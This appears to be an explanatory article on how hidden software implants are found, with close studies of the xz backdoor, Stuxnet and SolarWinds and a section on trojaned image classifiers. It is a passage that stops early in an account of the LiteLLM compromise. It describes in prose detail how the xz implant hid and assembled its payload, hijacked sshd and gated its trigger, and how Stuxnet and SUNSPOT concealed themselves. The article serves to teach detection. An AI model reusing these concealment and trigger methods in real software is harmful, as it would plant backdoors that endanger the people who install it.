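# How hidden software implants are found: runtime anomalies, code review and the case of neural networks

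## What is a concealed implant, and how can one be found?

A concealed implant is malicious code that someone has hidden in software, firmware or a device that other people trust. Victims usually install it themselves, inside a program or update they had good reason to want, and it then runs with that program's permissions.

Three of the best-known implants were found by people investigating something unusual. In 2010 a customer in Iran complained of Windows computers that kept crashing and rebooting, and the antivirus programmer Sergey Ulasen and his colleagues traced the problem to the Stuxnet worm (Kaspersky, 2011, *The Man Who Found Stuxnet*). In late 2020 the security company FireEye investigated an alert that an employee's account had registered a second phone, and eventually found an implant in SolarWinds' network management product, Orion (Mandia, 2021, *Prepared Statement of Kevin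 Mandia, CEO of FireEye, Inc*). In 2024 a developer investigating why remote logins over SSH used so much processor time found a backdoor in the compression package xz and announced it on a public mailing list (Freund, 2024, *backdoor in upstream xz/liblzma leading to ssh server compromise*). None of these discoveries began with someone reading source code, even though xz is open source and anyone could have read it.

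Three famous cases are not a representative sample, and Thomas and Francillon make a contrary claim in *Backdoors*, that people still find the vast majority of real-world backdoors by laborious manual analysis. The two observations may be compatible, because the investigators of SolarWinds and xz also had to take code apart by hand before they could say what they had found. The odd behaviour gave them a reason to start and a place to look.

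### Implants, payloads and triggers

A very small example shows most of the parts of an implant. *ROSA* (Kokkonis, Marcozzi and colleagues, 2025), a paper on automated backdoor detection, describes a hypothetical implant in sudo, the Unix command that lets an authorised user run a program as another user after typing a password. The original code checks the password and stores the result. The attacker then adds code that changes the result to "success" if the password is "let_me_in". Anyone who knows the phrase has full control of every machine that runs this copy of sudo.

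This implant is a backdoor, an implant that gives secret access. A trigger is the input, date or environment that makes an implant act, and here it is the phrase. The payload is the part that does the intended harm, here the instruction that overwrites the result. Real implants also tend to contain a lot of other code that installs, spreads or hides the payload.

An implant is dormant until its trigger occurs. Sometimes the trigger is the passage of time. FireEye's *Highly Evasive Attacker Leverages SolarWinds Supply Chain to Compromise Multiple Global Victims* describes malware that waited up to two weeks after the infected update was installed before first trying to reach its operators. The xz backdoor would run commands only for someone who held one particular private cryptographic key, according to *On the critical path to implant backdoors* (2024), so no tester could have found the right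 input by chance.

An implant differs from an accidental vulnerability in intent, though both can give an intruder the same access. *Backdoor* (Zdziarski, 2016) proposes a test based on intent, consent and access, and counts a mechanism as a backdoor only if it meets all three criteria. Intent is hard to establish because code rarely contains direct evidence of it. A debugging login that a programmer forgot to remove may look identical to one that a programmer planted. Concealment helps to establish intent, because carelessness does not easily explain a scrambled script inside a compression library's supposed test file.

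### From source code to a running program

Programmers keep source code and the history of its changes in a repository. Each recorded change is called a commit. When a version is ready, the maintainers publish a release, often as a compressed archive that Unix users call a tarball. The archive may differ from the repository. Many Unix projects use a tool that generates a configuration script for the build, and *The xz attack shell script* explains that they usually put this script and its supporting files only in the archive.

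In the next step, the build, a compiler translates the source into a binary, the file of machine instructions that a computer executes. The build also pulls in dependencies, which are packages written by other people. The publisher may then sign the binary, adding a cryptographic mark that lets recipients check who issued the file and whether anyone has changed it since. Users receive it as a download or as an update to a program they already have.

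An attacker can get in at any of these points. The cases below come from SLSA's *Supply chain threats*, a page of an industry specification for protecting this chain. The last column follows from how each attack worked.

| Point of entry | Case | What a reader of the repository would see |
|---|---|---|
| Producer | SpySheriff, a supposed anti-spyware program that was itself malicious | Nothing, if the producer keeps the source closed |
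| Authoring | A contractor for SushiSwap committed code that redirected cryptocurrency to themself | The malicious change |
| Repository server | An attacker broke into PHP's server and added two commits | The malicious changes |
| Build | Intruders at SolarWinds altered the program during each build | Clean code |
| Publication | An attacker with leaked credentials uploaded a malicious file to Codecov's download storage | Clean code |
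| Dependency | An attacker published a malicious binary of a package that event-stream used, without changing that package's source | Clean code, in both projects |

An implant's source code may be present only briefly, as it was in the SolarWinds case. CrowdStrike's *SUNSPOT* describes a tool that checked every second whether SolarWinds' build server was compiling Orion. When it was, the tool swapped one source file for a malicious version, waited for the compiler to finish, and put the original back, so a developer who opened the file afterwards would have found nothing wrong with it.

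The attacker split the xz implant. Most of it was in the public repository, disguised as compressed test files, which a compression project would naturally have. Freund reported that the line that unpacked and ran them was only in the release archives. A reader of the repository would therefore have seen opaque data files and no code that used them.

In his 1983 lecture *Reflections on Trusting Trust*, Ken Thompson, one of the creators of Unix, described an implant that can persist without appearing in source code. He altered a compiler to insert a backdoor whenever it compiled the login program, and to reinsert both alterations whenever it compiled a clean copy of its own source. After one build, the attacker can restore the original source, and the altered compiler will pass the implant on to each new version it compiles. *Running the “Reflections on Trusting Trust” Compiler* (2023) repeats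 the experiment with Thompson's own code, which consists of 99 lines and a 20-line script. From the same clean source, the original compiler produced a file of 10,724 bytes and the altered one a file of 12,918 bytes.

### Four routes to discovery

In source review, people or programs read source code to judge whether it is safe. This can catch a malicious commit, but not code that enters later in the chain. Kokkonis and colleagues say that auditing for backdoors takes such long and painstaking inspection that often nobody does it.

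An analyst who has only the binary can reverse engineer it, which means working out what a compiled program does without its source code. This can reveal an implant even when the source repository is clean, because the analyst examines the code that actually runs. The work is laborious. FireEye examined 4,000 executable files and decompiled millions of lines of code, converting machine instructions back into something closer to source, before it isolated the SolarWinds implant. The Record's *Sen. Warner Says U.S. ‘Underestimate[s] and Underreport[s]’ on Russian Hacks* quotes Mandia as saying that thousands of hours of forensic work came first, and that only this work had persuaded the company to take the SolarWinds software apart. Few organisations could do the same for every program they buy.

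Integrity checks take less work. They compare a file or record with a trusted reference and show that something has changed, but not what the change does. Their results are reliable only if the reference is. SolarWinds signed the altered Orion software and sent it out through its own update system (Krebs on Security, 2021), so a customer who checked the signature would have found it valid. Stuxnet's drivers also carried genuine certificates, which Ulasen's team concluded were stolen.

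A more demanding integrity check is to rebuild the program from its source and compare the result with the published binary, bit for bit. This works only if the build is reproducible, meaning that the same source always yields the same file. Even a timestamp or a directory name in the output can make the files differ. Rebuilding Orion from clean source on a clean machine should have exposed the swapped file, but rebuilding xz from its release archive would not have helped, because the archive already contained the implant. Thompson's compiler requires a special version of the check, called diverse double-compiling. The tester builds the suspect compiler's source with both the suspect compiler and a second, independent one, then compares what the two resulting compilers produce. *Running the “Reflections on Trusting Trust” Compiler* notes that almost no one checks that the binaries they receive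 match the source.

The remaining way to find an implant is to notice a runtime anomaly, an observed departure from expected behaviour in a running system, such as a delay, a crash, odd traffic or an unexpected log entry. This doesn't require suspecting an implant beforehand or having the source code. It does require someone who knows what normal behaviour looks like and cares enough to investigate departures from it, most of which are harmless. Ulasen's first guess was a misconfigured copy of Windows or a conflict between programs. Mandia noted that new phone registrations are common whenever a popular model comes out. A detector's false positive rate is the share of harmless events it flags, and a high rate soon wears out the people who must respond to its alerts.

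Dormancy limits this route too. Kokkonis and colleagues assembled 17 backdoors, seven authentic and ten synthetic, and every one changed the program's system calls (its requests to the operating system) when triggered. They argue that a backdoor can't do anything useful outside the program without changing these calls. Before the trigger arrives, though, the payload need not change them. They also point out that a well-coded backdoor should not crash the program even when it acts.

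### Alert, tracing and confirmation

Finding an implant takes three steps: an alert, when someone notices something suspicious; tracing, which locates the cause; and confirmation that the code responsible is malicious. Each step can use a different method. At FireEye, an anomaly in the login records raised the alert. Investigators then traced the cause through forensic work on the company's network and confirmed that the code was malicious by reverse engineering it.

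Discoveries can also stall after tracing, before the implant is confirmed. The security firm Volexity, investigating a breach at a think tank, deduced that a SolarWinds server was the likely source. It could not establish how the intruders had used the server, so it did not take the matter to SolarWinds, SecurityWeek reported, and the implant stayed in place.

Thompson arranged for another Unix group to take a copy of his compiler, which contained an implant. The group noticed that the compiler grew each time it compiled itself, because a bug added one extra byte to the implant's stored copy of its own text. This alerted them to a problem, and they broke the copying mechanism and ended up with a clean compiler. But according to Thompson's 2023 account, they never learned what they had removed.

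The file grew because of the code that carried the implant into each new compiler, not because of the payload, which was the login backdoor. For any discovery, it is useful to ask whether the sign came from the payload, the code that installs or spreads it, the code that conceals it, or the operators' own conduct. The FireEye alert came from the operators' conduct, since one of them had enrolled a phone.

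The cause of a sign affects when an implant can be found. If only payloads gave signs, every dormant implant would go unnoticed until its payload ran. Signs caused by installation or concealment may expose an implant before its trigger occurs, but a more careful author could have fixed the fault and left no sign. Signs from the operators' conduct appear only once they are using their access, and tracing an intruder back to a particular piece of software can take many steps.

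### Neural networks with hidden triggers

A neural network is a mathematical function that turns one list of numbers, such as the pixels of a photograph, into another, such as a score for each type of road sign. It does so in layers of simple units called neurons. Each neuron multiplies the outputs of the previous layer by a set of numbers called weights, adds the results together with a constant, and passes the sum through a simple non-linear function. Its output is its activation. Gu, Dolan-Gavitt and Garg (2017), in *BadNets*, write the whole of layer $i$ as

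$$a_i = \phi(w_i a_{i-1} + b_i)$$

where $a$ stands for the activations, $w$ for the weights, $b$ for the constants and $\phi$ for the non-linear function. Training is the process that sets the weights: a program adjusts them so as to shrink the gap between the network's answers and the correct answers on a large set of examples. Once training ends the weights stay fixed, while the activations differ with every input.

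A trojaned network is one that somebody has trained or altered to behave normally except when its input contains a trigger. Gu and colleagues built one that read American road signs and classified a stop sign as a speed limit sign if it bore a small sticker. They poisoned the training set by adding pictures with the trigger and the wrong label, so the network learned both to read ordinary signs correctly and to misclassify signs with the trigger. They assumed that a customer would pay someone else to train the network and accept it only if it scored well on pictures the customer had held back. The trojaned network passes this test because those pictures contain no stickers. With a yellow Post-it note as the trigger, accuracy on ordinary signs fell by less than one percentage point.

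A toy version with invented numbers makes the mechanism visible. Take a classifier that should call any sign with a small yellow sticker a speed limit. Suppose that one of its neurons responds only to a small yellow square, with an activation of 0 when there is none and 5 when there is one, and that a weight of 4 connects this neuron to the score for "speed limit". A clean stop sign gets 12 points for "stop" and 3 for "speed limit", and the extra neuron adds nothing. Put a sticker on it and "speed limit" gains 5 × 4 = 20 points and wins, 23 to 12. A million clean photographs would never reveal this. (A real network need not keep its sticker detector in a single neuron, which makes it harder to find.)

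A reviewer can read the ordinary code around such a network. It specifies the number of layers and how to multiply the weights, and it can be identical for a clean network and a trojaned one. In the scenario that Gu and colleagues studied, the customer chooses this structure, so the attacker can change only the weights. *DeepPayload* (2021) notes that a network consists of neurons and synapses where a program has instructions and variables, so a backdoor in a network needs a different definition. No line of text corresponds to the "let_me_in" comparison in sudo. The network may have millions of weights, which no programmer wrote and which mean very little individually. The training data is the nearest thing to source code, but a customer who downloads a finished network may never see it. A valid signature on the weights file would not rule out a backdoor if the trainer is the attacker.

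The methods therefore differ from those for software. Behavioural testing checks only a model's outputs on chosen inputs, and in the toy case it works if one of those inputs has a sticker. Weight inspection examines the learned numbers for signs of a trojan, such as the connection of strength 4 from a neuron with no evident purpose. Activation monitoring examines the intermediate values while the network processes an input, and could detect the neuron's jump from 0 to 5 when the input shows a stickered sign.

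## How did slow SSH logins expose the xz backdoor?

SSH is the usual way to log in to a Unix machine over a network, and sshd is the server program that handles these logins. In March 2024 Andres Freund, a developer of the PostgreSQL database, was running small timing tests on a Debian system and wanted as little other activity as possible, since it would disturb his measurements. He saw that sshd was using a surprising amount of processor time, even though the logins responsible were failing immediately because of wrong usernames and should have required very little work.

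In *A backdoor in xz*, on the Linux news site LWN, andresfreund (2024) corrected a reader who supposed that a slow login had caught his attention. He hadn't noticed any delay while logging in. He had run a profiler, which samples where a program spends its time. Much of the time went to liblzma, xz's library, and he became suspicious because the profiler could not match the code there to any named function. He then remembered that valgrind, a tool that checks how a program uses memory, had reported an odd error in his automated PostgreSQL tests a few weeks earlier, after some package updates. He wrote that the discovery "really required a lot of coincidences."

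Freund later reported in his post to the oss-security mailing list that a deliberately failed login took 0.299 seconds before the backdoored library was installed and 0.807 seconds afterwards. The client program used 0.202 seconds of processor time in both cases, so the extra half second must have come from the server.

### Comparing two runs of the same program

When Freund first started sshd by hand, the slowdown disappeared. It returned when systemd, the Linux program that starts and manages services, launched the server as usual. The cause was a difference in environment variables, the named settings that a program receives when it starts. Freund found that the backdoor acted only if TERM, which terminals normally set, was absent, LANG was present, two variables used for debugging were absent, and the program's name was /usr/sbin/sshd. The backdoor also seemed to detect the debugger rr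 and, in some situations, gdb. Securelist's *XZ backdoor story*, an analysis from Kaspersky's research site, also describes a kill switch, an environment variable with a long nonsense name and value that stopped the implant altogether.

These checks could easily have misled an investigator, because the problem disappeared when sshd was run from an ordinary terminal. Once Freund knew about them, he could switch the backdoor on and off. He ran sshd with an option that makes it print a help message and exit, which let him reproduce the fault without a network connection or a login. On his older system, this took about 0.5 seconds with only LANG set and about 0.01 seconds with TERM added. The half second roughly matches the delay in the failed login, because sshd starts a fresh copy of itself for each connection and so repeated the delay at every login.

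Freund then used a feature of Intel processors that records each branch a program takes, and compared runs with the backdoor active and inactive to find where they diverged. Two runs of the same program should follow the same path until an instruction tests a condition that differs between them. Finding that instruction narrows the search from a whole server and its libraries to a small stretch of code. He set breakpoints in gdb shortly before the divergence and worked forward from there.

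Freund said he was not a security researcher or reverse engineer, and most of what he reported came from watching the code run. Florian Weimer was the first to isolate the malicious object code (compiled code that has yet to be joined to the rest of a program). Freund at first assumed someone had compromised Debian's package, so he sent Debian a preliminary report. When he found the same material in xz's own releases, he decided not to file a bug with the project because someone inside it appeared to be involved. He published his findings on 29 March, a day after alerting Debian.

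### How the build assembled the implant

The release archives of xz 5.6.0 and 5.6.1 contained build-to-host.m4, one of the support files used to generate a project's configuration script. The attacker had added a few lines to the genuine version of this file. *The xz attack shell script* explains the whole build line by line.

The added lines search the source directory for a file with a line ending in four hash signs, five letters or digits, and four more hash signs. The only match is a supposedly corrupt test file named bad-3-corrupt_lzma2.xz. The attacker had corrupted it reversibly by swapping a few byte values, such as those for tabs and spaces. The build swaps them back, decompresses the file and runs the short script inside.

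That script opens a second test file, good-large_compressed.lzma, which decompresses normally but holds useful data mixed with junk. In version 5.6.1 the script throws away 1,024 bytes and keeps the next 2,048, does this sixteen times, and takes a further 939 bytes after one more discard. This yields

$$16 \times 2048 + 939 = 33{,}707 \text{ bytes.}$$

The last 31,233 of those bytes go through a simple substitution cipher and another round of decompression, which produces a much longer script. *The xz attack shell script* suggests that the cipher was there in case someone extracted exactly those bytes, because they would not look like compressed data until decoded.

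The long script first checks several conditions and stops silently if any of them fails. The target must be a Linux system with a 64-bit x86 processor, the compiler must be gcc, the linker (the program that joins compiled pieces together) must be GNU's, and the build must be producing a Debian or RPM package. Freund thought the last condition was probably meant to hinder investigators, because someone who just downloaded and compiled xz would get a clean library.

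If its checks pass, the script adds lines throughout the Makefile, the file that controls compilation, so that the script runs again while the library is being built. This time it decrypts the malicious object code from the same test file. It feeds an edited copy of one of xz's source files directly to the compiler, so the original on disk never changes. It then merges the malicious object into the result. The SolarWinds attack used a similar trick, but here the substitution happens when the users' own distributions build the library.

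### What happened each time sshd started

OpenSSH's server, sshd, does not itself use the compression library liblzma. But Debian and several other distributions modify sshd to notify systemd when it is ready, using a systemd library that loads liblzma. This loaded the attacker's code into the memory of sshd, which authenticates SSH logins.

The malicious code still needed a way to run. Liblzma has a faster version of its checksum function for processors with certain instructions. A feature called ifunc (indirect function) lets a library choose between versions at start-up by running a small function called a resolver. Liblzma's resolver checks what the processor supports by calling `__get_cpuid`. The attacker's edit removed one underscore, as Securelist points out, so the resolver instead called `_get_cpuid`, a function in the malicious object.

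Programs find functions in other libraries through a table of addresses, which a program called the dynamic linker fills in. In sshd, the linker fills in the whole table at start-up, then makes it read-only so that nobody can redirect the calls later. The resolvers run while the linker is still filling in the table, so this protective measure caused the attacker's code to run early enough to change the table.

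The malicious function was called twice, once for each of two checksum types. The first call did little except increase a counter. The second checked the environment and, if the conditions were met, searched the symbol tables, which list function names and their addresses, for the functions the implant needed. "This is the quite slow step that made me look into the issue," Freund wrote. The implant then attached a hook to the dynamic linker so that the linker reported each name it looked up. When the linker reported `RSA_public_decrypt`, the implant replaced that function's address with one of its own and removed the hook.

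The delay that exposed xz thus came from the backdoor installing itself, so it occurred even if the payload never ran and no attacker connected. It recurred every time sshd started on an affected machine, which gave people many chances to notice it.

The way the implant hid function names may have contributed to the delay. Securelist found that it recognized the functions it was looking for by number, which kept suspicious names out of the file. It ran each name through a trie, a tree that matches text one character at a time, and compared the resulting number with a stored constant. For example, `system`, the function that runs a command, gave 0x9F8. One of the search routines had to do this for every symbol in a library, which is a plausible reason for the slowness. Neither Freund nor Securelist reports timing the trie separately, so the half second may have had another cause.

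### A lock with one key

`RSA_public_decrypt` checks signatures when someone logs in with an RSA key, a common type of cryptographic key. Freund saw that the implant had taken over this function, but he did not yet know what the implant was checking for. Within a day, Patrakov (2024), in *Re: backdoor in upstream xz/liblzma*, passed on a preliminary account by Filippo Valsorda, who had been watching other people reverse engineer the code. According to Valsorda, the backdoor ran commands on the server for someone who had not logged in.

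An SSH client can present a certificate, which includes the public key of whoever signed it. The server has to process that key before it has accepted the login. An RSA public key consists mostly of one very large number, the modulus, and an attacker can fill it with any data they like. The implant treated the modulus as a possible message from its owner. It began by reading three fields, $a$, $b$ and $c$, and calculating

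$$t = ab + c.$$

It continued only if $t$ was 0, 1, 2 or 3, and this value also selected the command. The fields $a$ and $b$ have 32 bits each and $c$ has 64. If the sum wraps around at 64 bits, a random modulus is equally likely to produce any of the $2^{64}$ values of $t$, so it passes the check with probability $4/2^{64} = 2^{-62}$, or about one in 4.6 billion billion.

A message that passed still needed a valid signature. Securelist's *XZ backdoor*, the third part of the same series, describes how the implant decrypted the rest of the message and verified it against a public key that the attacker had built in, so only the holder of the matching private key could have signed it. The signed data also included the server's fingerprint, so a researcher who recorded a genuine message could not replay it against a different machine. The built-in key was also hard to find because the attacker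 had spread it over 456 ordinary-looking machine instructions, with one bit in each.

If any check failed, the implant let the login proceed as usual. Freund's recording of an ordinary key login shows sshd entering the malicious code, which then calls the real cryptographic library. So parts of the implant ran during normal logins, but the payload never did. Valsorda concluded that nobody could write a scanner that reliably detected the implant over the network unless the implant had a bug. Detecting it was easier with access to the machine, and Freund's post included a script by Vegard Nossum for doing so.

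The server's logs wouldn't have helped much once the attacker began using the backdoor. Securelist found that the backdoor could record a successful login as a failed attempt and suppress most other log messages.

### How the attacker became a maintainer

Lasse Collin had designed the .xz format in the 2000s with help from others, and he maintained the software as an unpaid hobby. *Wolves in the Repository* (2025), a software engineering study of the attack, describes the project as low-traffic, with a single developer and around ten active members in its chat channel.

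According to *Timeline of the xz open source attack* (2024), someone calling themself Jia Tan sent a first, harmless patch in October 2021. More useful patches followed, and in April 2022 other correspondents began to complain that Collin was slow to accept them. In early June "Jigar Kumar" said that there would be no progress without a new maintainer. Collin replied that long-term mental health problems, among other things, had limited his capacity, and that Jia Tan might take on a larger role. About two weeks later "Dennis Ens" acknowledged those problems and suggested that Collin hand over part of the work. By the end of the month Collin was calling Jia Tan practically a co-maintainer. Many of the complainers' addresses appear nowhere else on the internet, even in leaked data, and the *Timeline* concludes that they were probably fakes created to put pressure on Collin.

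Jia Tan was committing directly to the repository by the end of 2022 and published a first release, 5.4.2, in March 2023. That June another otherwise unknown contributor, "Hans Jansen", proposed the ifunc feature that the backdoor would later need. The stated reason was a small gain in speed, and Collin himself reworked the final change. In July Jia Tan turned ifunc off in the builds used by Google's oss-fuzz, a service that finds bugs by feeding programs large numbers of unusual inputs. Jia Tan claimed that ifunc was incompatible with one of the service's checking tools. According to the *Timeline*, the change may have been innocent.

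The test files went into the repository on 23 February 2024, and version 5.6.0 followed a day later. Over the next month Jia Tan pressed Fedora and Ubuntu to adopt the new release, and Jansen reappeared to urge Debian to do the same. The release reached Debian's unstable and testing branches and pre-release versions of Fedora.

### The valgrind errors

Others besides Freund saw signs of trouble. On 4 March, valgrind began reporting errors in Red Hat's distributions. *Timeline of the xz open source attack* places the errors in `_get_cpuid`, the backdoor's entry point. According to Freund, errors and crashes occurred in some configurations because the stack, the memory where a program keeps its temporary data, was not laid out as the implant required.

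Jia Tan handled the errors as a diligent maintainer would. A commit on 8 March supposedly fixed them, but the *Timeline* calls it a misdirection. Jia Tan made the real fix the next day by replacing the two test files. Jia Tan wrote in the commit message that the originals contained random data from a local machine and that the new ones used a constant seed so that others could reproduce them. Version 5.6.1 came out the same day with the revised implant and a new mechanism for finding further scripts in future test files, so the attacker would not need another excuse to replace old ones.

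A real bug made this deception easier, because people were already discussing one genuine ifunc problem and could more readily dismiss a second set of strange errors from the same area. Users of the Gentoo distribution had seen failures since 24 February. Hackaday's *Security Alert*, written just after the disclosure, counts these as an early sign of the backdoor and notes that Jia Tan blamed the compiler. The *Timeline* attributes them to an ordinary fault in the new ifunc code. The *Timeline*'s explanation is more likely, since Gentoo's sshd did not load the systemd library and the malicious script stopped unless it was building a Debian or RPM package.

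The valgrind reports came 24 days before Freund's alert and pointed to the right function, but they didn't expose the implant because the people who received them took them to Jia Tan, a maintainer they trusted, who was the attacker. Freund traced the code himself. He then used the false fixes as evidence against a break-in to Jia Tan's computer, which he considered unlikely because the committer had spent weeks discussing those fixes on mailing lists.

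### How much of it was luck?

Valsorda thought the backdoor had been "caught by chance", while Oxide and Friends, a podcast on which Freund later appeared, credits his habit of digging into details. Both explanations are fair. Freund happened to be running benchmarks on a system with the new library, but plenty of people would have stopped the sshd service and continued measuring. The valgrind error was also useful only because he remembered it.

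A reviewer could have found a clue in the repository without decoding the two new opaque files, because, as Freund noticed, no test in 5.6.0 used them. The files did not otherwise stand out, since the project's documentation had long said that many of its test files were created with a hex editor and had no better source. Checking which test needed the new files would have given a reviewer reason to ask Jia Tan some questions, though it would not have shown that the files were malicious.

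One piece of the sabotage was in plain text. In late February Jia Tan introduced a subtle typo into a tiny program that the build compiles to check for Landlock, a Linux feature for restricting what a program can do. The program never compiled, so the build always treated Landlock as missing. The commit lists Collin as the person who applied the change, and according to *Timeline of the xz open source attack*, he probably missed the typo. An experienced maintainer seems to have read a sabotaged change of a few lines and let it through, so more reading alone probably would not have exposed the better-hidden parts.

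Comparing the archive with the repository would have revealed build-to-host.m4, along with many legitimate files that only archives contain. The reviewer would then have had to compare build-to-host.m4 with the genuine file of the same name. *The xz attack shell script* calls the differences fairly plausible: a newer copyright year, a higher version number and a few obscure lines. Regenerating the build files might not have removed the attacker's version, because the usual tool appears to keep whichever copy has the higher serial number, and the attacker had raised the serial from 3 to 30. Building directly from the repository would have kept the backdoor out, because the test files do nothing without the script in the archive. Arch Linux switched to building this way on the day Freund alerted Debian.

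Two later articles consider whether better procedures would have caught the backdoor. *How NixOS and reproducible builds could have detected the xz backdoor* (Malka, 2025) argues that they could have. Someone would have had to build xz once from the archive and once from the repository and compare the results, since two builds from the same archive would match. They would also have had to do this while making a Debian or RPM package, because otherwise neither build would contain the implant. Otto Kekäläinen considers Debian's packaging practices in *Could the XZ backdoor have been detected*, and Open Source Security (2025), introducing an interview with him, describes the attack as nearly impossible to detect. These views conflict less than the titles suggest, because a person auditing the package would have had to recognise a few strange lines among thousands, while a mechanical comparison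 only needs to find that two files differ, although someone would still have had to investigate the difference.

Monitoring the build might also have exposed the backdoor. StepSecurity, which sells a monitoring tool, ran the compromised build under that tool and recorded the configuration step modifying the Makefile with a series of text-editing commands. The tampering was visible in the recording, but the company knew which file to look at, and configuration scripts routinely write Makefiles. The test is therefore little evidence that an analyst would have picked out those edits before the backdoor was known.

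The compiled library is harder to disguise completely because it has to contain the malicious code. *Binary Diff Summarization using Large Language Models* (2025) compares the library from version 5.6.0 with the one from 5.4.7. A language model summarises the functions that differ, and the same model or another then judges from the summaries whether the update is malicious. GPT5 correctly judged it malicious using either its own summaries or those of the smaller GPT5 mini. GPT5 mini did so using GPT5's summaries, but classified the update as benign when it used its own. The result is encouraging, but it is a single case, and the attack is famous enough that the models may have seen it in their training data.

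If the symbol search had been fast, Freund would have had no unusual processor use to investigate. The valgrind errors might still have led someone to the implant, but 5.6.1 was meant to remove them. The remaining signs would have been visible mainly to people who looked for them. In every affected sshd process, the table entry for `RSA_public_decrypt` pointed into a compression library, but few administrators check that entry. If the attacker had run a command, a shell would have appeared directly under the server in the process list, which is unusual, but only for as long as the command ran.

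The backdoor might also have lost its access to sshd without anyone discovering it. On 29 February a developer trimming systemd's dependencies proposed that its library stop linking to liblzma, and the project accepted the change on 5 March. According to *Timeline of the xz open source attack*, this change would apparently have defeated the attack once distributions adopted it. The *Timeline* also reports speculation that the attacker knew about the plan and hurried because of it. If so, the haste may help explain the bugs.

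*MergeShuffle* (2026) tests a way of disabling such code without first detecting it, by rebuilding a shared library around the parts that a program uses in normal operation. The experimenters started an SSH server with the compromised liblzma, logged in normally, and rebuilt the library from what that login had used. Normal logins still worked afterwards, but the backdoor connection failed. *MergeShuffle* concludes that the malicious code was removed, but the test shows only that the backdoor no longer worked. The implant's start-up code runs whenever sshd starts, so it could have counted as part of normal use and been kept. The code that only the attacker's key could reach would not have counted, because no ordinary login called it.

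## How did crashes expose Stuxnet and the LiteLLM malware?

A crash is easier to notice than half a second of processor time, but computers crash for so many ordinary reasons that few people would suspect an implant. In June 2010, support staff at VirusBlokAda, a small antivirus company in Belarus, passed Sergey Ulasen a complaint from a customer in Iran whose computers were crashing with a "blue screen", which Windows displays after a fatal error. The complaint led to the discovery of Stuxnet.

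Ulasen first suspected a misconfiguration or software conflict, so he asked for details of the software on the machines. He told Kaspersky that he changed his mind when he learned that many other computers on the network had the same fault. Some had a fresh copy of Windows, and a thorough check had found no junk applications on them.

This observation eliminated most of the ordinary explanations. Configuration errors and software conflicts tend to build up over time, and reinstalling Windows removes them. Failing hardware would be unlikely to affect many computers together. The cause had to be something the fresh machines had picked up since installation, probably from the network or a shared drive. A faulty driver that the customer installed everywhere could have produced the same pattern, so this wasn't proof of malware, but Ulasen had no doubt that malware was the cause. Since ordinary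 scans found nothing, he also suspected a rootkit, software that hides files and activity from the operating system's own tools.

The investigation depended on a friendship between Ulasen and the security expert in Iran who reported the problem. The expert had already tried to solve it alone and then with technical support, and he persisted because he had Ulasen's personal contact details. They spent a Saturday on the phone while Ulasen was at a wedding. On the Monday, Ulasen connected to an infected computer remotely and, after much effort, found the malicious files. Microsoft and Realtek, whose certificate the attackers had used, gave him no proper response, so he published his findings. Working out everything the worm did took much longer. In *Unravellling Stuxnet*, slides for a conference that September, Gostev and Raiu (2010) reported that the analysis at Kaspersky had occupied several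 teams for two months.

### What made the computers crash?

Ulasen did not name the technical fault in the interview. A reader asked in the comments whether one of Stuxnet's drivers, mrxcls.sys, had started too early and conflicted with other parts of Windows, but nobody answered. The cause still appears to be unsettled.

When a Windows computer crashes, a driver is a reasonable suspect, because drivers run in the kernel, the core of the operating system, where a serious error stops the whole machine. If an ordinary program makes a serious error, Windows can usually close it and carry on. Stuxnet installed two drivers. Antiy's *Comprehensive Analysis Report on the Stuxnet Worm Attack on Industrial Control Systems* describes how one of them, mrxnet.sys, hid the worm's files on USB drives. The other, mrxcls.sys, made sure the worm ran again after every restart.

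Chappell explains how this second driver worked in *The MRXCLS.SYS Malware Loader*. The driver registered with Windows to be notified whenever a program loaded. If the program was on its list, the driver altered the program's first instructions so that the worm's code would run before anything else. The list included services.exe, which runs on every Windows machine. A mistake in such code could easily crash a computer, but that is not evidence that this driver crashed any.

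Chappell also found that mrxcls.sys would not start in Safe Mode, the reduced version of Windows that technicians use to diagnose faults, or when kernel debugging was enabled. If this driver caused the blue screens, they would have disappeared when a technician was most likely to look for them. The xz delay had similarly disappeared when Freund ran sshd from a terminal.

### Sabotage behind normal readings

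Stuxnet's payload ran on programmable logic controllers, not on Windows. These small industrial computers, made by Siemens, controlled the machinery at the worm's target, the uranium enrichment plant at Natanz. Centrifuges there spin uranium gas at supersonic speed to separate its isotopes. The worm travelled on USB drives and through local networks until it reached a Windows computer that engineers used to program the controllers, and then added its own code to the controllers.

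The version of Stuxnet the attackers released in June 2009 changed the speed of the centrifuges, while an earlier one had manipulated valves to raise the pressure inside them. During an attack, the operators' screens kept showing readings from normal operation. Stuxnet also replaced a library file that Step 7, Siemens' programming software, used to communicate with the controllers. An engineer who read a controller's program back through Step 7 would not have seen the added code.

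The blue screens therefore came from the Windows part of Stuxnet, which spread and hid the worm. The attackers may have had less opportunity to test this part. *Stuxnet Dossier*, an analysis by the security company Symantec, says that they would have needed a replica of the plant's control equipment to test their code. A replica would have been ideal for testing code meant for one known installation, but the Windows part had to run on whatever computers the worm reached, with whatever software their owners had installed.

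The sabotage itself also produced a sign. Zetter's *An Unprecedented Look at Stuxnet, the World's First Digital Weapon* reports that in January 2010, inspectors from the International Atomic Energy Agency noticed centrifuges at Natanz failing at an unprecedented rate. The number enriching uranium had already fallen by 984 between June and November 2009, to 3,936. Natanz arranged its centrifuges in groups of 164, called cascades, so the drop equals exactly six cascades. Zetter cautions that some of the drop may have been a lingering effect of an earlier version of Stuxnet.

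This sign came five months before Ulasen's case and was much closer to the attackers' purpose, but nobody traced it to the code because the natural place to look was the centrifuges. Centrifuges can break for mechanical reasons, and Natanz had had trouble with them before. The Iranian technicians apparently understood the cause no better than the inspectors did. A technician who suspected the controls would have seen normal readings on the screen. The inspectors were there to monitor nuclear material and had little reason to analyze the plant's software.

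In July 2009, about two weeks after Stuxnet infected Neda Industrial Group, an Iranian maker of control systems, an engineer there wrote on a Siemens user forum that every PC at the company was reporting an error in a Step 7 library file. He suspected a virus on flash drives, because files copied from an affected computer to a clean one by CD or DVD caused no trouble, but copying them by flash drive gave the new computer the same fault. This was a better experiment than the one that convinced Ulasen, since it isolated the means of infection. But the company's virus scans found nothing, and nothing in the discussion suggests that anyone solved the problem. Ulasen knew from his work on anti-rootkit software that a clean scan did not rule out an infection, and he had remote access to an infected machine.

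### A start-up file that launched itself

In March 2026, a crash exposed an implant in LiteLLM much faster. LiteLLM is an open-source Python package that lets a program use language models from many companies through a single interface. People and automated systems install it 15 to 20 million times a week from PyPI, the public index of Python packages. PyPI's *Incident Report* (2026) traces the attack to an earlier compromise of Trivy, a security scanner that LiteLLM's developers used. That compromise exposed a token for publishing on PyPI.

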